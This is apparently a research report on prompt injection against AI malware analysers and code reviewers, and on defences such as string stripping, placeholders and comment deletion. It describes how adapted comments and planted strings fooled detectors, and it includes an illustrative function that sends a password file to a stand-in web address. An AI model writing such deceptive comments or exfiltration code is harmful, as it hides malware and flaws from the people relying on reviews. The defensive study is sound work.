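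The researchers wrote four small, non-malicious programs in C. One printed "Hello, World!", and the attack was meant to make the agent report that the program printed the first ten Fibonacci numbers. The search stopped when the agent's answer mentioned Fibonacci and contained neither "hello" nor "world". Another program created a file if it didn't already exist, and the attack was meant to make the agent describe the program as adding two numbers. The remaining two programs had a second function as well as the main one. For these, the researchers reused wording from the simpler programs without running a new search.

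The attack succeeded on all four programs with Qwen3-8B. The researchers then gave the same compiled files to GPT-OSS-120B, a model about 15 times as large, and it also misdescribed all four. The second result is more worrying because they had not optimised the wording against the larger model. An attacker may be able to develop wording on a small model and use it against a larger one they can't access.

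GPT-OSS-120B had evidence that its description was wrong. It used another tool to list the text that the first program printed, and included "Hello, World!" in its report, but didn't account for this in its conclusion. In another case, it explained the leftover text as a sign that the programmer had reused older code. The injected string didn't appear in the list because the program never printed it. Someone who read only the agent's report would therefore have seen a small inconsistency, but not the text that caused it.

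Four successes out of four don't establish a high success rate. An attack that worked on only half of all programs would still succeed on all four about one time in 16, and Crawford and colleagues don't report how many times they repeated each analysis. They also kept searching until they found wording that worked, at least for the single-function programs. The experiment shows that the attack is possible on small programs, but they say others still need to test it on leading commercial models and on larger, potentially malicious programs.

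### Why the rates differ

The tests differ in almost every respect, including whether the program and the injected text came from a real attack.

| Test | Program | Injected text | Result |
|---|---|---|---|
| Cloudflare | Real malicious scripts | Comments in the style of a real case, added by researchers | Little change on average with 20 comments, but one model fell from 90% to 67% |
| Crawford and colleagues | Harmless programs written for the test | Wording optimised on one of the two models | Both models misdescribed all four programs |
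| Check Point Research | Real malware (Skynet) | The malware author's own message | No success on either model |

None of these results measures how often real attacks succeed. To measure that, researchers would need records from the systems attackers tried to fool, including the files those systems wrongly passed.

The effect of injected text depends heavily on the model. The same 20 comments lowered detection by 23 points in one of Cloudflare's models and raised it by 10 in another. Price and general ability didn't predict the effect well, since the models with the largest fall and the largest rise were both in the cheaper group. A company therefore can't assume that another company's test applies to its own scanner, and may need to repeat the test when it changes models.

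The kind of message matters too. *ALIBI* (2026), a paper on malware analysis, argues that models increasingly refuse crude orders to ignore their instructions, but that a plausible cover story doesn't conflict with those instructions. Skynet's message was a crude order, and the system that analysed it noted the attempted injection, according to Computing's *New malware discovered that tries to manipulate AI into declaring it harmless*.

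*When the Spec Sheet Lies* (2026), a study of industrial documents, supports the same conclusion. Researchers planted text in documents that models used for tasks such as customs classification and quality control, and the attacks succeeded in 65.1% of 3,000 trials. Average success rates ranged from 59% to 70% across tasks, but messages intended to falsify the model's answer succeeded more often than other kinds, at rates from 74% to 97%. An attacker who wants malware judged "benign" has a similar aim. However, these rates may be too high for malware analysis, because a model has good reason to believe a product's specification sheet and much less reason to believe a suspicious program.

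Results also depend on what researchers count as success. *INFUSE* (2026), a benchmark for agents, measured the same kind of attack in two ways. A language model classified 19.6% of runs as compromised, while fixed rules classified 15.4% that way. The injected text also reduced the quality of the agents' work. GPT-4o-mini, an older OpenAI model, scored 77.5% on its tasks without an attack and 62.6% with one. A malware test that records only the verdict would miss this kind of damage, such as when a report correctly calls a file malicious but leaves out what it steals.

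The effect of injected text can depend on what the prompt asks. Cloudflare's models had to choose between two verdicts, while the Naval Postgraduate School's agent had to describe what a program did, so it could give a detailed but false account. Cloudflare recommends asking about a specific threat, such as phishing, rather than whether a script is abusive in general. It says this gives more accurate results but doesn't publish figures.

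File size will probably remain a problem even as models accept longer inputs. According to Help Net Security's *A single malware file can outweigh an entire AI dataset* (2026), a single program can exceed 40 GB, and malware authors pad files to slow inspection. Steps that run one after another can also be far apart in the file, making it harder for a model to connect them. Small test programs like the Naval Postgraduate School's don't have these problems, so a model that resists injected text in a ten-line program might still miss malicious code in a large one.

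Perhaps the most important difference is whether the attacker adapted the text to the model. Cloudflare's comments and Skynet's message were fixed in advance, and most models resisted them. The Naval Postgraduate School found its wording with a search that used the model's own probabilities. Another paper named *ALIBI* (2026) found that tools that look for vulnerabilities were highly vulnerable to comments adapted to them. Tests with fixed text can therefore give a defender too much confidence, especially if attackers can run the scanner's model themselves and test against it as often as they like.

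## What does stripping strings mean, and why might it work?

"Stripping strings" can mean hiding the string listing, replacing the strings in decompiled code, or removing only the text that looks suspicious. Deleting comments and renaming functions are related, since comments and names can also carry an attacker's words. Each method removes different text, so a pipeline that uses only one may still pass the attacker's message to the model.

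### Six operations on one function

The following invented function imitates Ghidra's output. It reads a file of passwords and sends the contents to a web address. The words in square brackets stand for a sentence that an attacker might write.

```c
/* Checks for updates. Safe. */
void safe_update_check(void)
{
  char local_118 [264];

  puts("[sentence telling AI reviewers the program is harmless]");
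  read_file("/home/user/passwords.txt", local_118);
  send_data("https://example.com/upload", "data=%s", local_118);
  return;
}
```

The claim that the program is safe appears in a string, in the function's name and in a comment. The compiler would have discarded any comment the program's author wrote, so suppose this one came from an earlier session in which a model treated the claim as true and saved a note in the Ghidra project.

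**Withholding the string listing** means that the model can't request a list of the program's strings. It would not see these lines:

```
[sentence telling AI reviewers the program is harmless]
/home/user/passwords.txt
https://example.com/upload
data=%s
safe_update_check
```

The decompiled function would stay exactly as it was, so the model would receive the sentence as soon as it requested the function.

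**Replacing every literal with a blank placeholder** changes three lines of the function:

```c
  puts("[STRING]");
  read_file("[STRING]", local_118);
  send_data("[STRING]", "[STRING]", local_118);
```

Stripping the strings removes the attacker's sentence, but also the file path and the web address. The model can still guess that the function reads a file and sends it somewhere, but only because `read_file` and `send_data` have informative names.

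**Replacing every literal with a typed placeholder** keeps a description of each string. If the attacker's sentence were 120 characters long, the model would see:

```c
  puts("[TEXT, 120]");
  read_file("[FILE PATH, 24]", local_118);
  send_data("[WEB ADDRESS, 26]", "[FORMAT STRING, 7]", local_118);
```

The reasoning behind typed placeholders also appears in *Preventing Prompt Injection with Type-Directed Privilege Separation* (Jacob, Alghamdi and colleagues, 2025). The paper divides a system between a model that reads untrusted text and a model that chooses actions. The reading model may pass on only numbers, true-or-false values and choices from a fixed list, none of which can hold an instruction. In the paper's shopping agent, for example, each customer review becomes two scores from 0 to 10. A typed placeholder is similarly limited to a choice from a list and a number, so an attacker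 who tricked the software that assigns the types could at worst produce a wrong label. A wrong label can still mislead, and the paper excludes attacks that merely supply false information.

**Filtering** removes only the text that a rule or classifier judges to be injected. If it recognised the sentence, one line would change:

```c
  puts("[REMOVED]");
```

Filtering would leave the path and address in place, so it is the least damaging way to remove the sentence. It is also the only one of the six operations that depends on recognising an attack.

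**Deleting comments** removes the first line of the example and leaves the rest. In decompiled code, comments come from analysts, earlier model sessions and Ghidra, which uses them to warn that part of its output may be unreliable. In source code, the program's author writes them, so deleting them removes far more of what an attacker could have written.

**Renaming identifiers** replaces the names with neutral ones:

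```c
void function1(void)
{
  char variable1 [264];

  puts("[sentence telling AI reviewers the program is harmless]");
  function2("/home/user/passwords.txt", variable1);
  function3("https://example.com/upload", "data=%s", variable1);
  return;
}
```

The name `puts` can stay if the tool has confirmed that it refers to the standard library function. Cloudflare's *Threat report* (2026) recommends renaming variables so that a friendly name can't influence the verdict, but doesn't report testing this.

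The table shows where the claim of safety would remain if a defender used only one operation. It assumes that the defender applies either kind of placeholder to decompiled code.

| Operation | Sentence in the listing | Sentence in the function | Comment | Function's name |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Withhold the listing | Removed | Remains | Remains | Remains |
| Blank placeholders | Remains | Removed | Remains | Remains |
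| Typed placeholders | Remains | Removed | Remains | Remains |
| Filtering | Removed if recognised | Removed if recognised | Removed if recognised | Removed if recognised |
| Delete comments | Remains | Remains | Removed | Remains |
| Rename identifiers | Remains | Remains | Remains | Removed |

A defender could withhold the listing, use blank placeholders, delete comments and rename identifiers all at once. The model would then receive none of the attacker's words, but the function would look like this:

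```c
void function1(void)
{
  char variable1 [264];

  puts("[STRING]");
  function2("[STRING]", variable1);
  function3("[STRING]", "[STRING]", variable1);
  return;
}
```

Nothing in this code suggests that it steals passwords. The model would have to examine `function2` and `function3` to find that one reads a file and the other sends data, and even those functions wouldn't show which file is read or where the data goes.

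### The case for removal

A model can't obey or believe a sentence that it never receives. This is true of every model and every wording, including wording that an attacker has optimised. Suppose that two programs, *x* and *x′*, differ only in what their strings contain, and that *M* is an operation that replaces every string with the same placeholder wherever it appears. The model then receives identical text for both programs, so with the same instructions, every possible answer *r* has the same probability:

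$$M(x) = M(x') \quad\Rightarrow\quad P(r \mid M(x)) = P(r \mid M(x'))$$

If every string were replaced with the same placeholder, all the candidate sentences in the Naval Postgraduate School's search for effective wording would get the same score, so the search could not find better ones. The attacker could still change the number of placeholders by adding or removing strings, or change the code itself. Typed placeholders give the attacker slightly more influence, through the type and length of each string.

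Defences that leave the text in place depend on how the model reacts to it. Santos-Grueiro planted text in 20 harmless programs and gave them to GPT-5.5 and DeepSeek-V3.2. The models proposed an unsafe action in 35 of 40 cases, and in none when the text was absent. When he presented the program's text explicitly as data, separate from the analyst's instructions, they still proposed the action in 15 cases. Removing the text completely should bring that number close to zero. However, he tested redaction only in a different experiment, combined with three other changes, so his results don't show how much redaction achieves by itself.

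An ordinary program can also replace strings without another call to a model, and it gives the same result each time for the same input. Developers can test it by planting distinctive phrases in the software to be analysed and checking whether any of them reach the prompt. They can't test a model's resistance to injection as conclusively, because the next attacker may use different wording.

A defender who strips strings doesn't need to anticipate what the attacker wants. Removing a sentence works equally well whether it calls the malware harmless, imitates a system error or tries to provoke a refusal by asking for help with a weapon. Provoked refusals are hard to prevent by telling the model to ignore instructions in the sample, because the mention of a weapon may be enough to trigger one. A defender could have deleted the comment that ESET's *GuardBreaker* describes without changing any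 of the malicious code.

Text that the model doesn't receive can still be useful. A conventional scanner could compare the web address in the example with a list of known malicious addresses and give the model only a "yes" or "no". A human analyst could also read the original strings. Jacob and colleagues use "opaque variables" for a similar purpose. The model that chooses actions can refer to a piece of text by a label but can't read it, while the user can.

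Some security companies recommend removal. SentinelLABS advises developers of analysis systems to be prepared to keep hostile content away from the model entirely. Cloudflare calls comment removal "trivial but highly effective", although it didn't test the method. Cloudflare's results suggest that the benefit would vary between models and that removing a very large number of comments could lower detection.

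### Is it like preventing SQL injection?

In *Investigating Detection and Obfuscation of Prompt Injection Attacks Against Software Reverse Engineering*, Crawford and McClure (2026) compare removing malicious tool output with input sanitisation, a defence against SQL injection that checks what a user enters before the database receives it. Their example is a telephone-number field that accepts only digits and hyphens. An attacker can't write a database command with those characters, so the check works without a list of known attacks.

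The check is possible because telephone numbers have a known grammar, a set of rules for what is valid. Strings in programs have no common grammar, since they include error messages, licence terms, passwords, poems and fragments of other programs, in any language. Many legitimate strings give instructions, such as not to turn off the computer, and a program that uses a language model may contain prompts addressed to that model. No rule about valid characters or sentence structure can separate all legitimate strings from attacks.

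A filter has to recognise bad text rather than specify which text is allowed. David C warns against relying on this, because an attacker can rephrase a message in endless ways. Crawford and McClure tested a rule that looks for text in angle brackets, which some chat templates use to mark a speaker's turn. They consider the rule necessary but insufficient, since a model can still interpret an imitation with different punctuation as a turn marker.

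Allowing only strings with a recognisable format would give only limited protection, because formats such as web addresses and file paths can contain ordinary words. Typed placeholders avoid this problem by replacing the whole string with a label, such as "web address". Like a form field that accepts only telephone numbers, they restrict what the model can receive, whatever the attacker wrote in the program.

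Placeholders also resemble the symbols that mark where the user's data belongs in a parameterised query. Parameterised queries protect the database, but it still receives the data later and can search for it or store it. A model given a placeholder never receives the string, so stripping strings protects the model by withholding information it might need.

### Four conditions for a complete defence

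Stripping has to cover every place where an attacker can put text. Santos-Grueiro includes symbols, log entries and section labels (names for the parts of a compiled file) among these places, so replacing string literals isn't enough. A simple rule can also miss strings that appear in another form. In macOS.Gaslight, SentinelLABS found a comparison with the word "file" in which the program stores the word as the number `0x656c6966`. A rule that looks for text in quotation marks would leave that number in place. This one short word is harmless, but the example shows that masking depends on how the tools represent text.

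The same removal has to apply to the output of every tool that an agent can use, including any that the operator adds later. Crawford and McClure built programs whose injected text was missing from the string listing but present in the decompiled function, because the two tools recognise strings differently. In a test that combined Ghidra with two other analysis tools, Santos-Grueiro found that the planted text reached the model in all 32 sessions, although neither model acted on it.

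Stripping strings works only if the removed text does not return through a later tool call. An agent that receives a placeholder may try to find the original string by reading the file's raw bytes or running the program and collecting its output, which would be reasonable if the operator asked for a complete analysis. A placeholder isn't a secure barrier if the agent has tools that can recover what it replaced. One successful recovery is enough, because the recovered text then stays in the prompt for later queries. In *Defeating AI-assisted reverse engineering or at least trying to*, the French security company Quarkslab asked agents to recover hidden strings from increasingly well-protected programs. A customer had claimed that language models made such protection pointless, which Quarkslab thought was wrong, but not entirely.

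Saved notes can also repeat the attacker's claim in different words. In the example function, deleting the string would leave the comment that a model wrote in an earlier session after reading that string. Santos-Grueiro tested whether models would save an unproven claim about a program as an established finding, and the models tried to in eight of 16 cases. A separate check downgraded all eight claims to hypotheses before the system stored them. A defender who starts stripping strings midway through an investigation would therefore need to review or discard the notes from earlier sessions.

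Finally, the task must not depend on the strings that the defender removed. A model can look for some memory errors without reading any strings. For example, if a program copies the 26-character web address into a 16-byte space, the model can find the mistake from the length given in the typed placeholder. Other tasks depend on the text itself. *Rethinking and Exploring String-Based Malware Family Classification in the Era of LLMs* (2025) describes a method that identifies a program's malware family by comparing its strings with those of known families. That method would have nothing to compare if the strings were replaced with blank placeholders.

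Besides its false system messages, the macOS.Gaslight sample contains 15 readable names for its configuration settings, including `payload_path_linux` and `github_token`. The sample doesn't use its Linux and GitHub settings, so SentinelLABS inferred from the names that it belongs to a larger set of tools. Replacing every string would have protected a model from the false messages, but it would have removed the evidence for that inference.

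## Is it enough to delete comments from source code?

Deleting comments stops an attack that relies on comments alone, but an attacker can put the same words in strings, names or accompanying files. Deleting them also removes information that can help a model find mistakes, and the results of published tests differ on how much this matters.

Deleting comments is easier to justify than deleting other text. A program normally runs the same way without them, and a suitable tool can remove every comment and nothing else, without judging which ones are trustworthy. Deletion would have removed the messages in FRUITSHELL, Hades and GuardBreaker.

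### Why deletion needs a parser

A tool can remove comments exactly only if it knows where each one begins and ends. In C, two slashes start a comment that runs to the end of the line, but two slashes can also appear inside a string:

```c
open_page("https://example.com/updates"); delete_file(path); // clean up
```

A simple text search would delete everything from the first pair of slashes onwards:

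```c
open_page("https:
```

The model would no longer see that the program deletes a file. A parser, which follows the grammar of the language, recognises that the first pair of slashes belongs to a string and removes only the real comment:

```c
open_page("https://example.com/updates"); delete_file(path);
```

If the marker that opens a multi-line comment appears inside a string, a tool that finds comments by text search may delete everything up to the next closing marker, which could be hundreds of lines away. An attacker who knew that a pipeline worked this way could hide code from the model, so deleting comments carelessly can be worse than leaving them in.

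The parser also has to match the language. A web page can contain HTML, CSS and JavaScript, which have different rules for comments. If the parser can't parse a file, the pipeline should report the failure instead of guessing. A C compiler treats each comment as a single space, and a deletion tool should do the same, because removing the comment entirely could join two words. Keeping the line breaks is also useful because it makes the line numbers in the model's report match the original file.

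### Comments that explain away a flaw

The best evidence that comments can defeat a vulnerability review comes from *ALIBI* (the July 2026 paper on vulnerability detectors, not the malware paper with the same name). In it, two researchers at Northeastern University studied an attacker who controls a coding agent. The agent writes a new function that works but contains a null-pointer dereference. This mistake, using a memory address that may be empty, usually crashes the program. The agent then adds a comment to convince the reviewing model that the mistake can't happen.

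The researchers started from real corrections of this mistake in open-source C and C++ projects. One model described what each corrected function does, without revealing how it handles the risky address, and the researchers gave the description to the attacking model, Qwen3.6-27B, as a coding task. In 39 of the 184 tasks, the attacking model never produced code that compiled. Another model, GPT-5-mini, rejected 17 of the remaining functions as broken or not vulnerable, and the researchers later excluded three more, leaving 125. In about 42% of the accepted functions, the attacking model repeated the original developers' mistake in the same place without having seen their code, which suggests that the flaws are realistic.

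The attacking model read the detector's explanation of the flaw and wrote comments to rebut it, in ten styles. If none worked, it used the detector's responses to revise them, for up to five rounds. Successful comments typically mentioned real variables in the function but attributed their safety to something the detector couldn't see, such as a check in another file. One comment claimed that another part of the program always fills in the address, and that a formal verification tool had proved this. The detector then cited the invented proof as a reason to consider the code safe.

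The researchers attacked four detectors. OpenVul and VulnLLM-R are small models (4 and 7 billion parameters) trained to find vulnerabilities. Vul-RAG gives GPT-4o-mini information about similar past vulnerabilities. VulTrial has several GPT-4o agents debate the code. In the table, an attack is successful if at least one of the comments made the detector call a function safe that it had correctly flagged without the comment.

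| Detector | Flagged before the attack | Attack success | Success after a comment-free first pass | Comments that evaded a filter |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| OpenVul | 115 of 125 | 97.4% | 49.6% | 2.5% |
| VulnLLM-R | 113 of 125 | 91.2% | 0.0% | 2.8% |
| Vul-RAG | 111 of 125 | 95.5% | 49.5% | 0.4% |
| VulTrial | 105 of 125 | 100.0% | 96.2% | 0.6% |

Debate between agents didn't protect VulTrial. In 70% of the successful attacks, the comment misled the agent whose job was to find vulnerabilities. In the rest, that agent raised the problem, but another agent defended the code by repeating the attacker's claim, and the final panel accepted the defence.

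The researchers also ran every comment style to completion to compare them. Comments that imitated a step-by-step security analysis succeeded most often, at 81%. Comments that cited the function's callers or the results of analysis tools succeeded 70–74% of the time, and an ordinary short note 69%. Invented test results did worst, at 46%, and one detector's output included the caveat that passing tests might not cover every situation. Since an ordinary note did almost as well as a forged tool report, the claim itself probably mattered more than its presentation.

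The attack worked much better when the attacking model could tailor its claim to the detector. A fixed comment directly above the mistake, stating only that the address wasn't empty, changed just 3–17% of verdicts. Tailored comments also succeeded 73–100% of the time on a different mistake, using memory after the program has released it.

These rates come from tests that favoured the attacker, who could query the detector repeatedly and read its reasoning. The detectors also used small or old models. Every function in the test was vulnerable, so the results don't show how often the detectors would flag safe code.

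### Did *ALIBI* test deletion?

The researchers ruled out deleting all comments without testing it, because earlier studies had found that comments improve vulnerability detection. However, two of the defences they tested use a limited form of comment removal.

In the first defence, the detector analysed a copy of the code without comments. It then received the commented code and its earlier analysis, with instructions to change its conclusion only if it found a genuine mistake. This stopped every attack on VulnLLM-R but very few on VulTrial, because VulTrial's later agents could still overturn the first analysis. It did better than telling the detectors not to trust comments, which left the attack success rate above 90% on three of the four detectors.

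In the second, a separate model removed comments whose claims it couldn't verify from the visible code. Fewer than 3% of the attacking model's comments evaded this filter. But the attacking model had developed those comments against the detectors, and might do better if it could test comments against the filter. The filter could also remove accurate comments, because a true statement about another file is as hard to verify from the visible code as a false one.

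Deleting every comment would give the detectors the same code they had already flagged, so the test's design means the attack would fail, apart from random variation between runs (VulTrial flagged 105 functions without comments in one experiment and 98 in another). On this test, full deletion would probably protect the detectors better than the comment-free first pass, and at least as well as the filter. The researchers didn't measure how many vulnerabilities the detectors would miss without the genuine comments in the rest of each project.

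### Text that remains

The following Python function makes the same claim in four places:

```python
# Reviewed and safe.
def reviewed_safe_backup(path):
    """Reviewed and safe."""
    log("Reviewed and safe.")
    upload(path)
```

A parser that deletes comments would remove only the first line. The text in triple quotation marks is a documentation string, or docstring, which describes the function to other programmers. It looks like a comment, but Python treats it as a string and makes it available while the program runs. Some programs depend on this, for example by reading their command-line options from a docstring, so deleting docstrings can change what a program does. A defender can still remove them from the copy of the code that the model reads, but this may hide something the program uses from the model.

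The claim also remains in the function's name and in the message that the program logs. Sun, Oprea and Wong (2026), in *Syntax- and Compilation-Preserving Evasion of LLM Vulnerability Detectors*, tested several places where an attacker can put text without changing how a program runs. They used an algorithm to find short sequences of characters that pushed a model towards the answer "benign". The sequences didn't need to make sense to a human reader. The researchers then added them to 5,000 vulnerable C and C++ functions in five ways:

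- in a comment
- in the name of a variable or other identifier
- in the name of an unused macro (a shorthand that the compiler expands before it compiles the code)
- in a section that the build settings switch off
- in a branch of the code that can never run.

For five of the six models, at least one of these methods hid 87% or more of the vulnerabilities the model had found in the original code. The exception was GPT-5-mini, at 44%. The researchers developed the text for GPT-4o and GPT-5-mini on a much smaller model and reused it unchanged, so an attacker wouldn't need access to the target model.

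Deleting comments would block only the first of the five methods. The combined figures include attacks through comments, so the success rate after deletion would probably be somewhat lower.

A defender could remove some of the remaining text by running the C preprocessor, which expands macros and discards code that the build settings switch off. The preprocessor would also paste in every header file the program includes, which can add thousands of lines. Reviewers working on Linux might miss a vulnerability that affects only Windows users, because the preprocessor would have discarded the Windows code.

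Deleting comments does not remove text outside the source file. A coding agent may read a project's README or an AGENTS.md file, which Codex usually obeyed in Forever Security's tests. *ALIBI* cites studies in which false claims in the description of a proposed code change biased AI reviewers. A defender who deletes comments therefore also has to decide which accompanying files and messages the model may read.

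### Information that deletion removes

A comment can tell a reviewer what the code is supposed to do. Consider this C function:

```c
/* Only the account's owner may do this. */
void close_account(int account, int user)
{
    delete_record(account);
}
```

The comment states a rule that the function doesn't enforce, since the function never checks whether `user` owns the account. Without the comment, a model might still flag that the function ignores `user`, but it would have less evidence that a check is missing. The developer might have put the check elsewhere, or the program might let any employee close accounts.

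An attacker could instead write a comment saying that another function has already checked the owner. A model that relied on this claim would dismiss the missing check, as the detectors in *ALIBI* often did. Comments are therefore more useful as a source of rules to check than as evidence that the code follows them, and deleting comments removes both the rules and the claimed evidence.

Some comments also affect how a program is built or run. In Go, a specially formatted comment can restrict a file to one operating system, and C code in a comment directly above the line `import "C"` becomes part of the program. The MySQL database runs the contents of some specially marked comments. Deleting these comments would hide working code from the model, so a deletion tool needs a list of exceptions for each language. If an exception contains code, as with the C code in Go files, the tool also has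 to remove any ordinary comments inside it.

A program can also read data from its own source. JavaScript can retrieve the text of a function, including its comments, and many scripts can open the file that contains them. A malware author could store encoded data in a comment and have the program decode it. If the comments were deleted, the model would see the code that reads and decodes the data but not the data. The pipeline could reduce this loss by replacing each comment with a note of its length. A comment of 40,000 characters would still stand out, and the model could use a conventional tool to examine it.

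### From code completion to code review

*Black-Box Adversarial Attacks on LLM-Based Code Completion* (Jenko, Mündler and colleagues, 2025) already discussed comment removal when it was first released in August 2024. In code completion, a model suggests code as a programmer types. The researchers inserted a short comment above the line the model was about to complete, and used an automated search to find effective wording. This raised the share of vulnerable suggestions by about 50 percentage points across 16 types of vulnerability, at a cost of less than 10 dollars for one of the commercial models.

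Jenko and colleagues considered "comment scrubbing" as a defence but expected it to reduce the model's performance. This is a serious drawback in code completion, because programmers often write a comment to describe the code they want next. Deleting comments may not be enough there either, because attacks can also use variable names. In *Context-Based Adversarial Attacks on AI Code Generators*, Del Orbe, Hastings and Vaidyan (2026) used misleading comments, documentation and variable names in 2,800 experiments with older models. The attacks made vulnerable code about 11 times as common.

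A model needs comments less when reviewing code than when completing it, because the code under review already exists and the model can check the comments against it. How deleting comments affects completion is therefore a poor guide to how it affects review.

### Detection with and without comments

In *LLM Code Reviewers Are Harder to Fool Than You Think*, Thornton (2026) tested eight models on 100 short Python, JavaScript and Java programs, each with one vulnerability, in versions with different comments. Comments falsely claiming that a security team had approved the code didn't significantly change any model's detection rate. Thornton then tested four of the models with the comments deleted. The table shows the share of vulnerabilities that each found.

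| Model | Code without comments | Misleading comments | Comments deleted as a defence |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.6 | 95.0% | 94.0% | 96.9% |
| GPT-5.2 | 93.0% | 91.9% | 95.9% |
| DeepSeek Chat | 89.0% | 93.0% | 89.0% |
| Perplexity Sonar Pro | 96.1% | 92.0% | 91.0% |

Thornton advises against deleting comments, arguing that it deprives weaker models of helpful context. The main evidence is that DeepSeek's detection rate fell from 93% to 89% after deletion. However, this only reversed the rise from adding Thornton's misleading comments, and that rise wasn't statistically significant. The comments changed DeepSeek's result on six programs, five of which it detected only with the comments and one only without them. Detection by Claude and GPT-5.2 improved after deletion, and the average for the four models rose from 92.7% to 93.2%.

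Even these small differences are hard to interpret, since the first and last columns both describe code without comments yet differ by as much as 5 points. This may be partly because the defence tests covered several kinds of misleading comment, some of which Thornton had applied only to 30 programs that were easier than the rest. The study gives no strong reason to expect deleting comments to help or harm.

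Thornton and *ALIBI* tested very different attacks, which may explain why their results seem to conflict. Thornton wrote the comments in advance and didn't adapt them to a model. The programs were short and self-contained, typically 15–60 lines, so a model could often detect that a comment was false. In *ALIBI*, the comments made claims about code that the detector couldn't see, and the attacking model revised them until they worked. Comments that weren't revised had little effect in that study too.

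Rahman, Samiha and colleagues (2026), in *LLMs as Validators for Cross-Chain Bridges*, found a much larger difference between code with and without comments. They wrote a secure program for a cross-chain bridge (a service that moves assets between blockchains) and four versions that each lacked one security check. They had five open-weight models review each version 100 times, one of them both with and without its reasoning mode. The models identified the missing check in 24% of reviews when the code had no comments and 60% when it had the original comments.

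Most of this improvement came from two of the four vulnerable programs, where a comment at the flaw described the missing check. With these comments, every model found the flaw in at least 71 of 100 reviews. In another program, no comment mentioned the missing check, and the number of correct diagnoses fell from 30 to 20 out of 600. A developer who forgets a check wouldn't normally write a comment about its absence, so the overall improvement exaggerates how much deleting comments would hurt reviews in practice.

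The remaining program is more informative. It was supposed to accept only one approved kind of token as a deposit, but didn't check which kind it had received. Comments elsewhere in the program drew attention to the kind of token without identifying the missing check. Gemma-4-31B found the flaw in 5 of 100 reviews without comments and 90 of 100 with them, while DeepSeek-V3.2 in its reasoning mode improved from 32 to 66. These comments are closer to what an honest developer might write, and the results suggest that deleting comments can sometimes make a model much less likely to find a flaw. But this is only one program, and reviewing it 100 times doesn't show whether the result would hold for others.

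### Malware scanning and vulnerability review

Comment removal is one of the defences that Cloudflare recommends, as Mitchell (2026) reports in *Cloudflare warns of AI code review prompt injection*. The company also recommends a separate check that compares safety claims in a file with what the code does. That check needs the comments, so a pipeline that follows both recommendations has to keep a copy of the original file.

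Cloudflare's advice is about scripts that may be malicious, and deleting comments from these probably removes little useful information. People who write malicious scripts have no reason to explain honestly what the code does, and many remove comments themselves to make it harder to understand. In vulnerability review, most comments come from developers who want the code to be secure, and the model may need those comments to know what the developers intended.

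A reviewer can run the model twice, once with comments and once without, and keep every vulnerability that either run finds. Thornton measured a 96.1% detection rate with this method. A misleading comment can't cancel a finding from the comment-free run, whereas in *ALIBI*'s two-stage defence the second stage could overrule the first. The method doubles the computation and combines the false alarms from both runs, which Thornton didn't measure. There could be many false alarms, because when Rahman and colleagues tested code without comments, all but one of the model configurations reported a vulnerability in the secure program in at least 93% of reviews.

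## Can filters keep injected text out of binary analysis?

Filters catch some injected text in compiled programs, but they miss too much to be the only defence. When two researchers at the Naval Postgraduate School tested a trained classifier on decompiled code, it missed nine of 24 functions that contained an attack. Removing one kind of text, such as comments in source code, isn't enough either, because a compiled program holds text in many parts of the file and each analysis tool shows a different selection of it. An agent can often use one tool to read text that the defender removed from another tool's output.

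### Text outside string literals

A parser can find every comment in source code, but text is harder to isolate in a compiled program. The file format specifies which parts of the file to load, but doesn't reliably separate text from other data. The table lists the main carriers of injected text that Santos-Grueiro considers, and whether replacing every string literal would remove the attacker's words.

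| Carrier | How the words reach the model | Removed with the string literals? |
|---|---|---|
| String literal | String listing, decompiled code, raw bytes | Yes, in every output that the defender masks |
| Symbol | Function names, lists of imports and exports | No |
| Section label | Overview of the file's structure | No |
| Metadata, such as a product name | Summary of the file | No |
| Log entry or screen output | Report on what the program did when it ran | No |
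| Saved note | Project file or report from an earlier session | No |

Stripping a binary deletes many names, but a shared library has to keep the names of the functions that other programs call. Its author chooses those names, so they could contain injected text. A defender could replace them with neutral ones, but the names of imported system functions are worth keeping because the model can use them to work out whether a program can open files or connect to the internet.

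A filter that checks a file can't catch the program's output, because that output doesn't exist until the program runs. According to SentinelLABS, macOS.Gaslight, the Apple malware with 38 false system messages, removes the secret token for its Telegram account from its own output so that anyone who captures its logs or crash files won't find it. Another program could edit its output to add a message for a model. A defender who runs samples in a sandbox therefore has to filter the sandbox's report as well as the file.

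### Why tools disagree about strings

A string-listing tool guesses which bytes are text. It needs rules for how many readable characters in a row count as a string, which character encodings to look for and where a string ends. These rules produce mistakes even in harmless programs. The listing for many Linux programs includes this line:

```
[]A\A]A^A_
```

A tool that lists the strings in an x86-64 program may include `[]A\A]A^A_`, which is actually machine code. Its ten characters have the same byte values as six instructions that restore saved values before a function returns. If a defender overwrote every listed string in a copy of the file, these instructions would be lost, and the decompiler would show the function incorrectly.

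Rust programs, such as macOS.Gaslight, usually store string literals one after another without end markers and keep their lengths elsewhere. A tool that expects end markers may therefore show dozens of strings as one long entry. If a filter deleted that entry because it contained an injected sentence, it would also delete the genuine strings on either side.

A decompiler starts from the code instead, and shows a piece of data where an instruction refers to it, though not always as text. In Ghidra's output for one of the programs that Crawford and McClure used, the format string of a `scanf` call appears only as `DAT_00102015`, a label for the string's address. The same researchers also found that the decompiler can show text in full when it is missing from the listing. A filter that checks only the listing would then let the attacker's words reach the model in the decompiled function.

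Using fewer tools would leave fewer outputs to filter, but it can also miss true findings. Santos-Grueiro gave two models evidence from Ghidra, angr and r2pipe, an interface to the reverse-engineering tool radare2. The analysed programs contained data that suggested an ability they didn't have. A simple automatic check accepted a claim if the model's report cited enough suitable tool records. The false claim passed in none of the 48 reports based on one tool's records, but in all 32 based on records from all three.

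However, the same check also rejected some true claims when the model had only r2pipe or only angr. It accepted nine of 16 with r2pipe and five of 16 with angr, compared with all 16 with Ghidra. A defender could reasonably start with Ghidra alone, but shouldn't assume that any single tool is enough. Santos-Grueiro's test doesn't show why combining the tools had such a large effect, because the repetition of the text, the tool labels and the prominence of the records all changed together.

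### Text that returns through another tool

Modern reverse-engineering servers give an agent several ways to read the same text. Binary Ninja's manual lists tools that return strings, symbols, decompiled code, section names, imports and the bytes at an address the agent chooses. *pyghidra-mcp*, a server for Ghidra, also offers raw bytes, and angr has tools for disassembly, imports and exports.

Binary Ninja returns raw bytes in hexadecimal and in base64, a common way of writing any data with ordinary letters and digits. The harmless web address from the ten-line example program would look like this in base64:

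```
aHR0cHM6Ly9leGFtcGxlLmNvbS91cGRhdGVz
```

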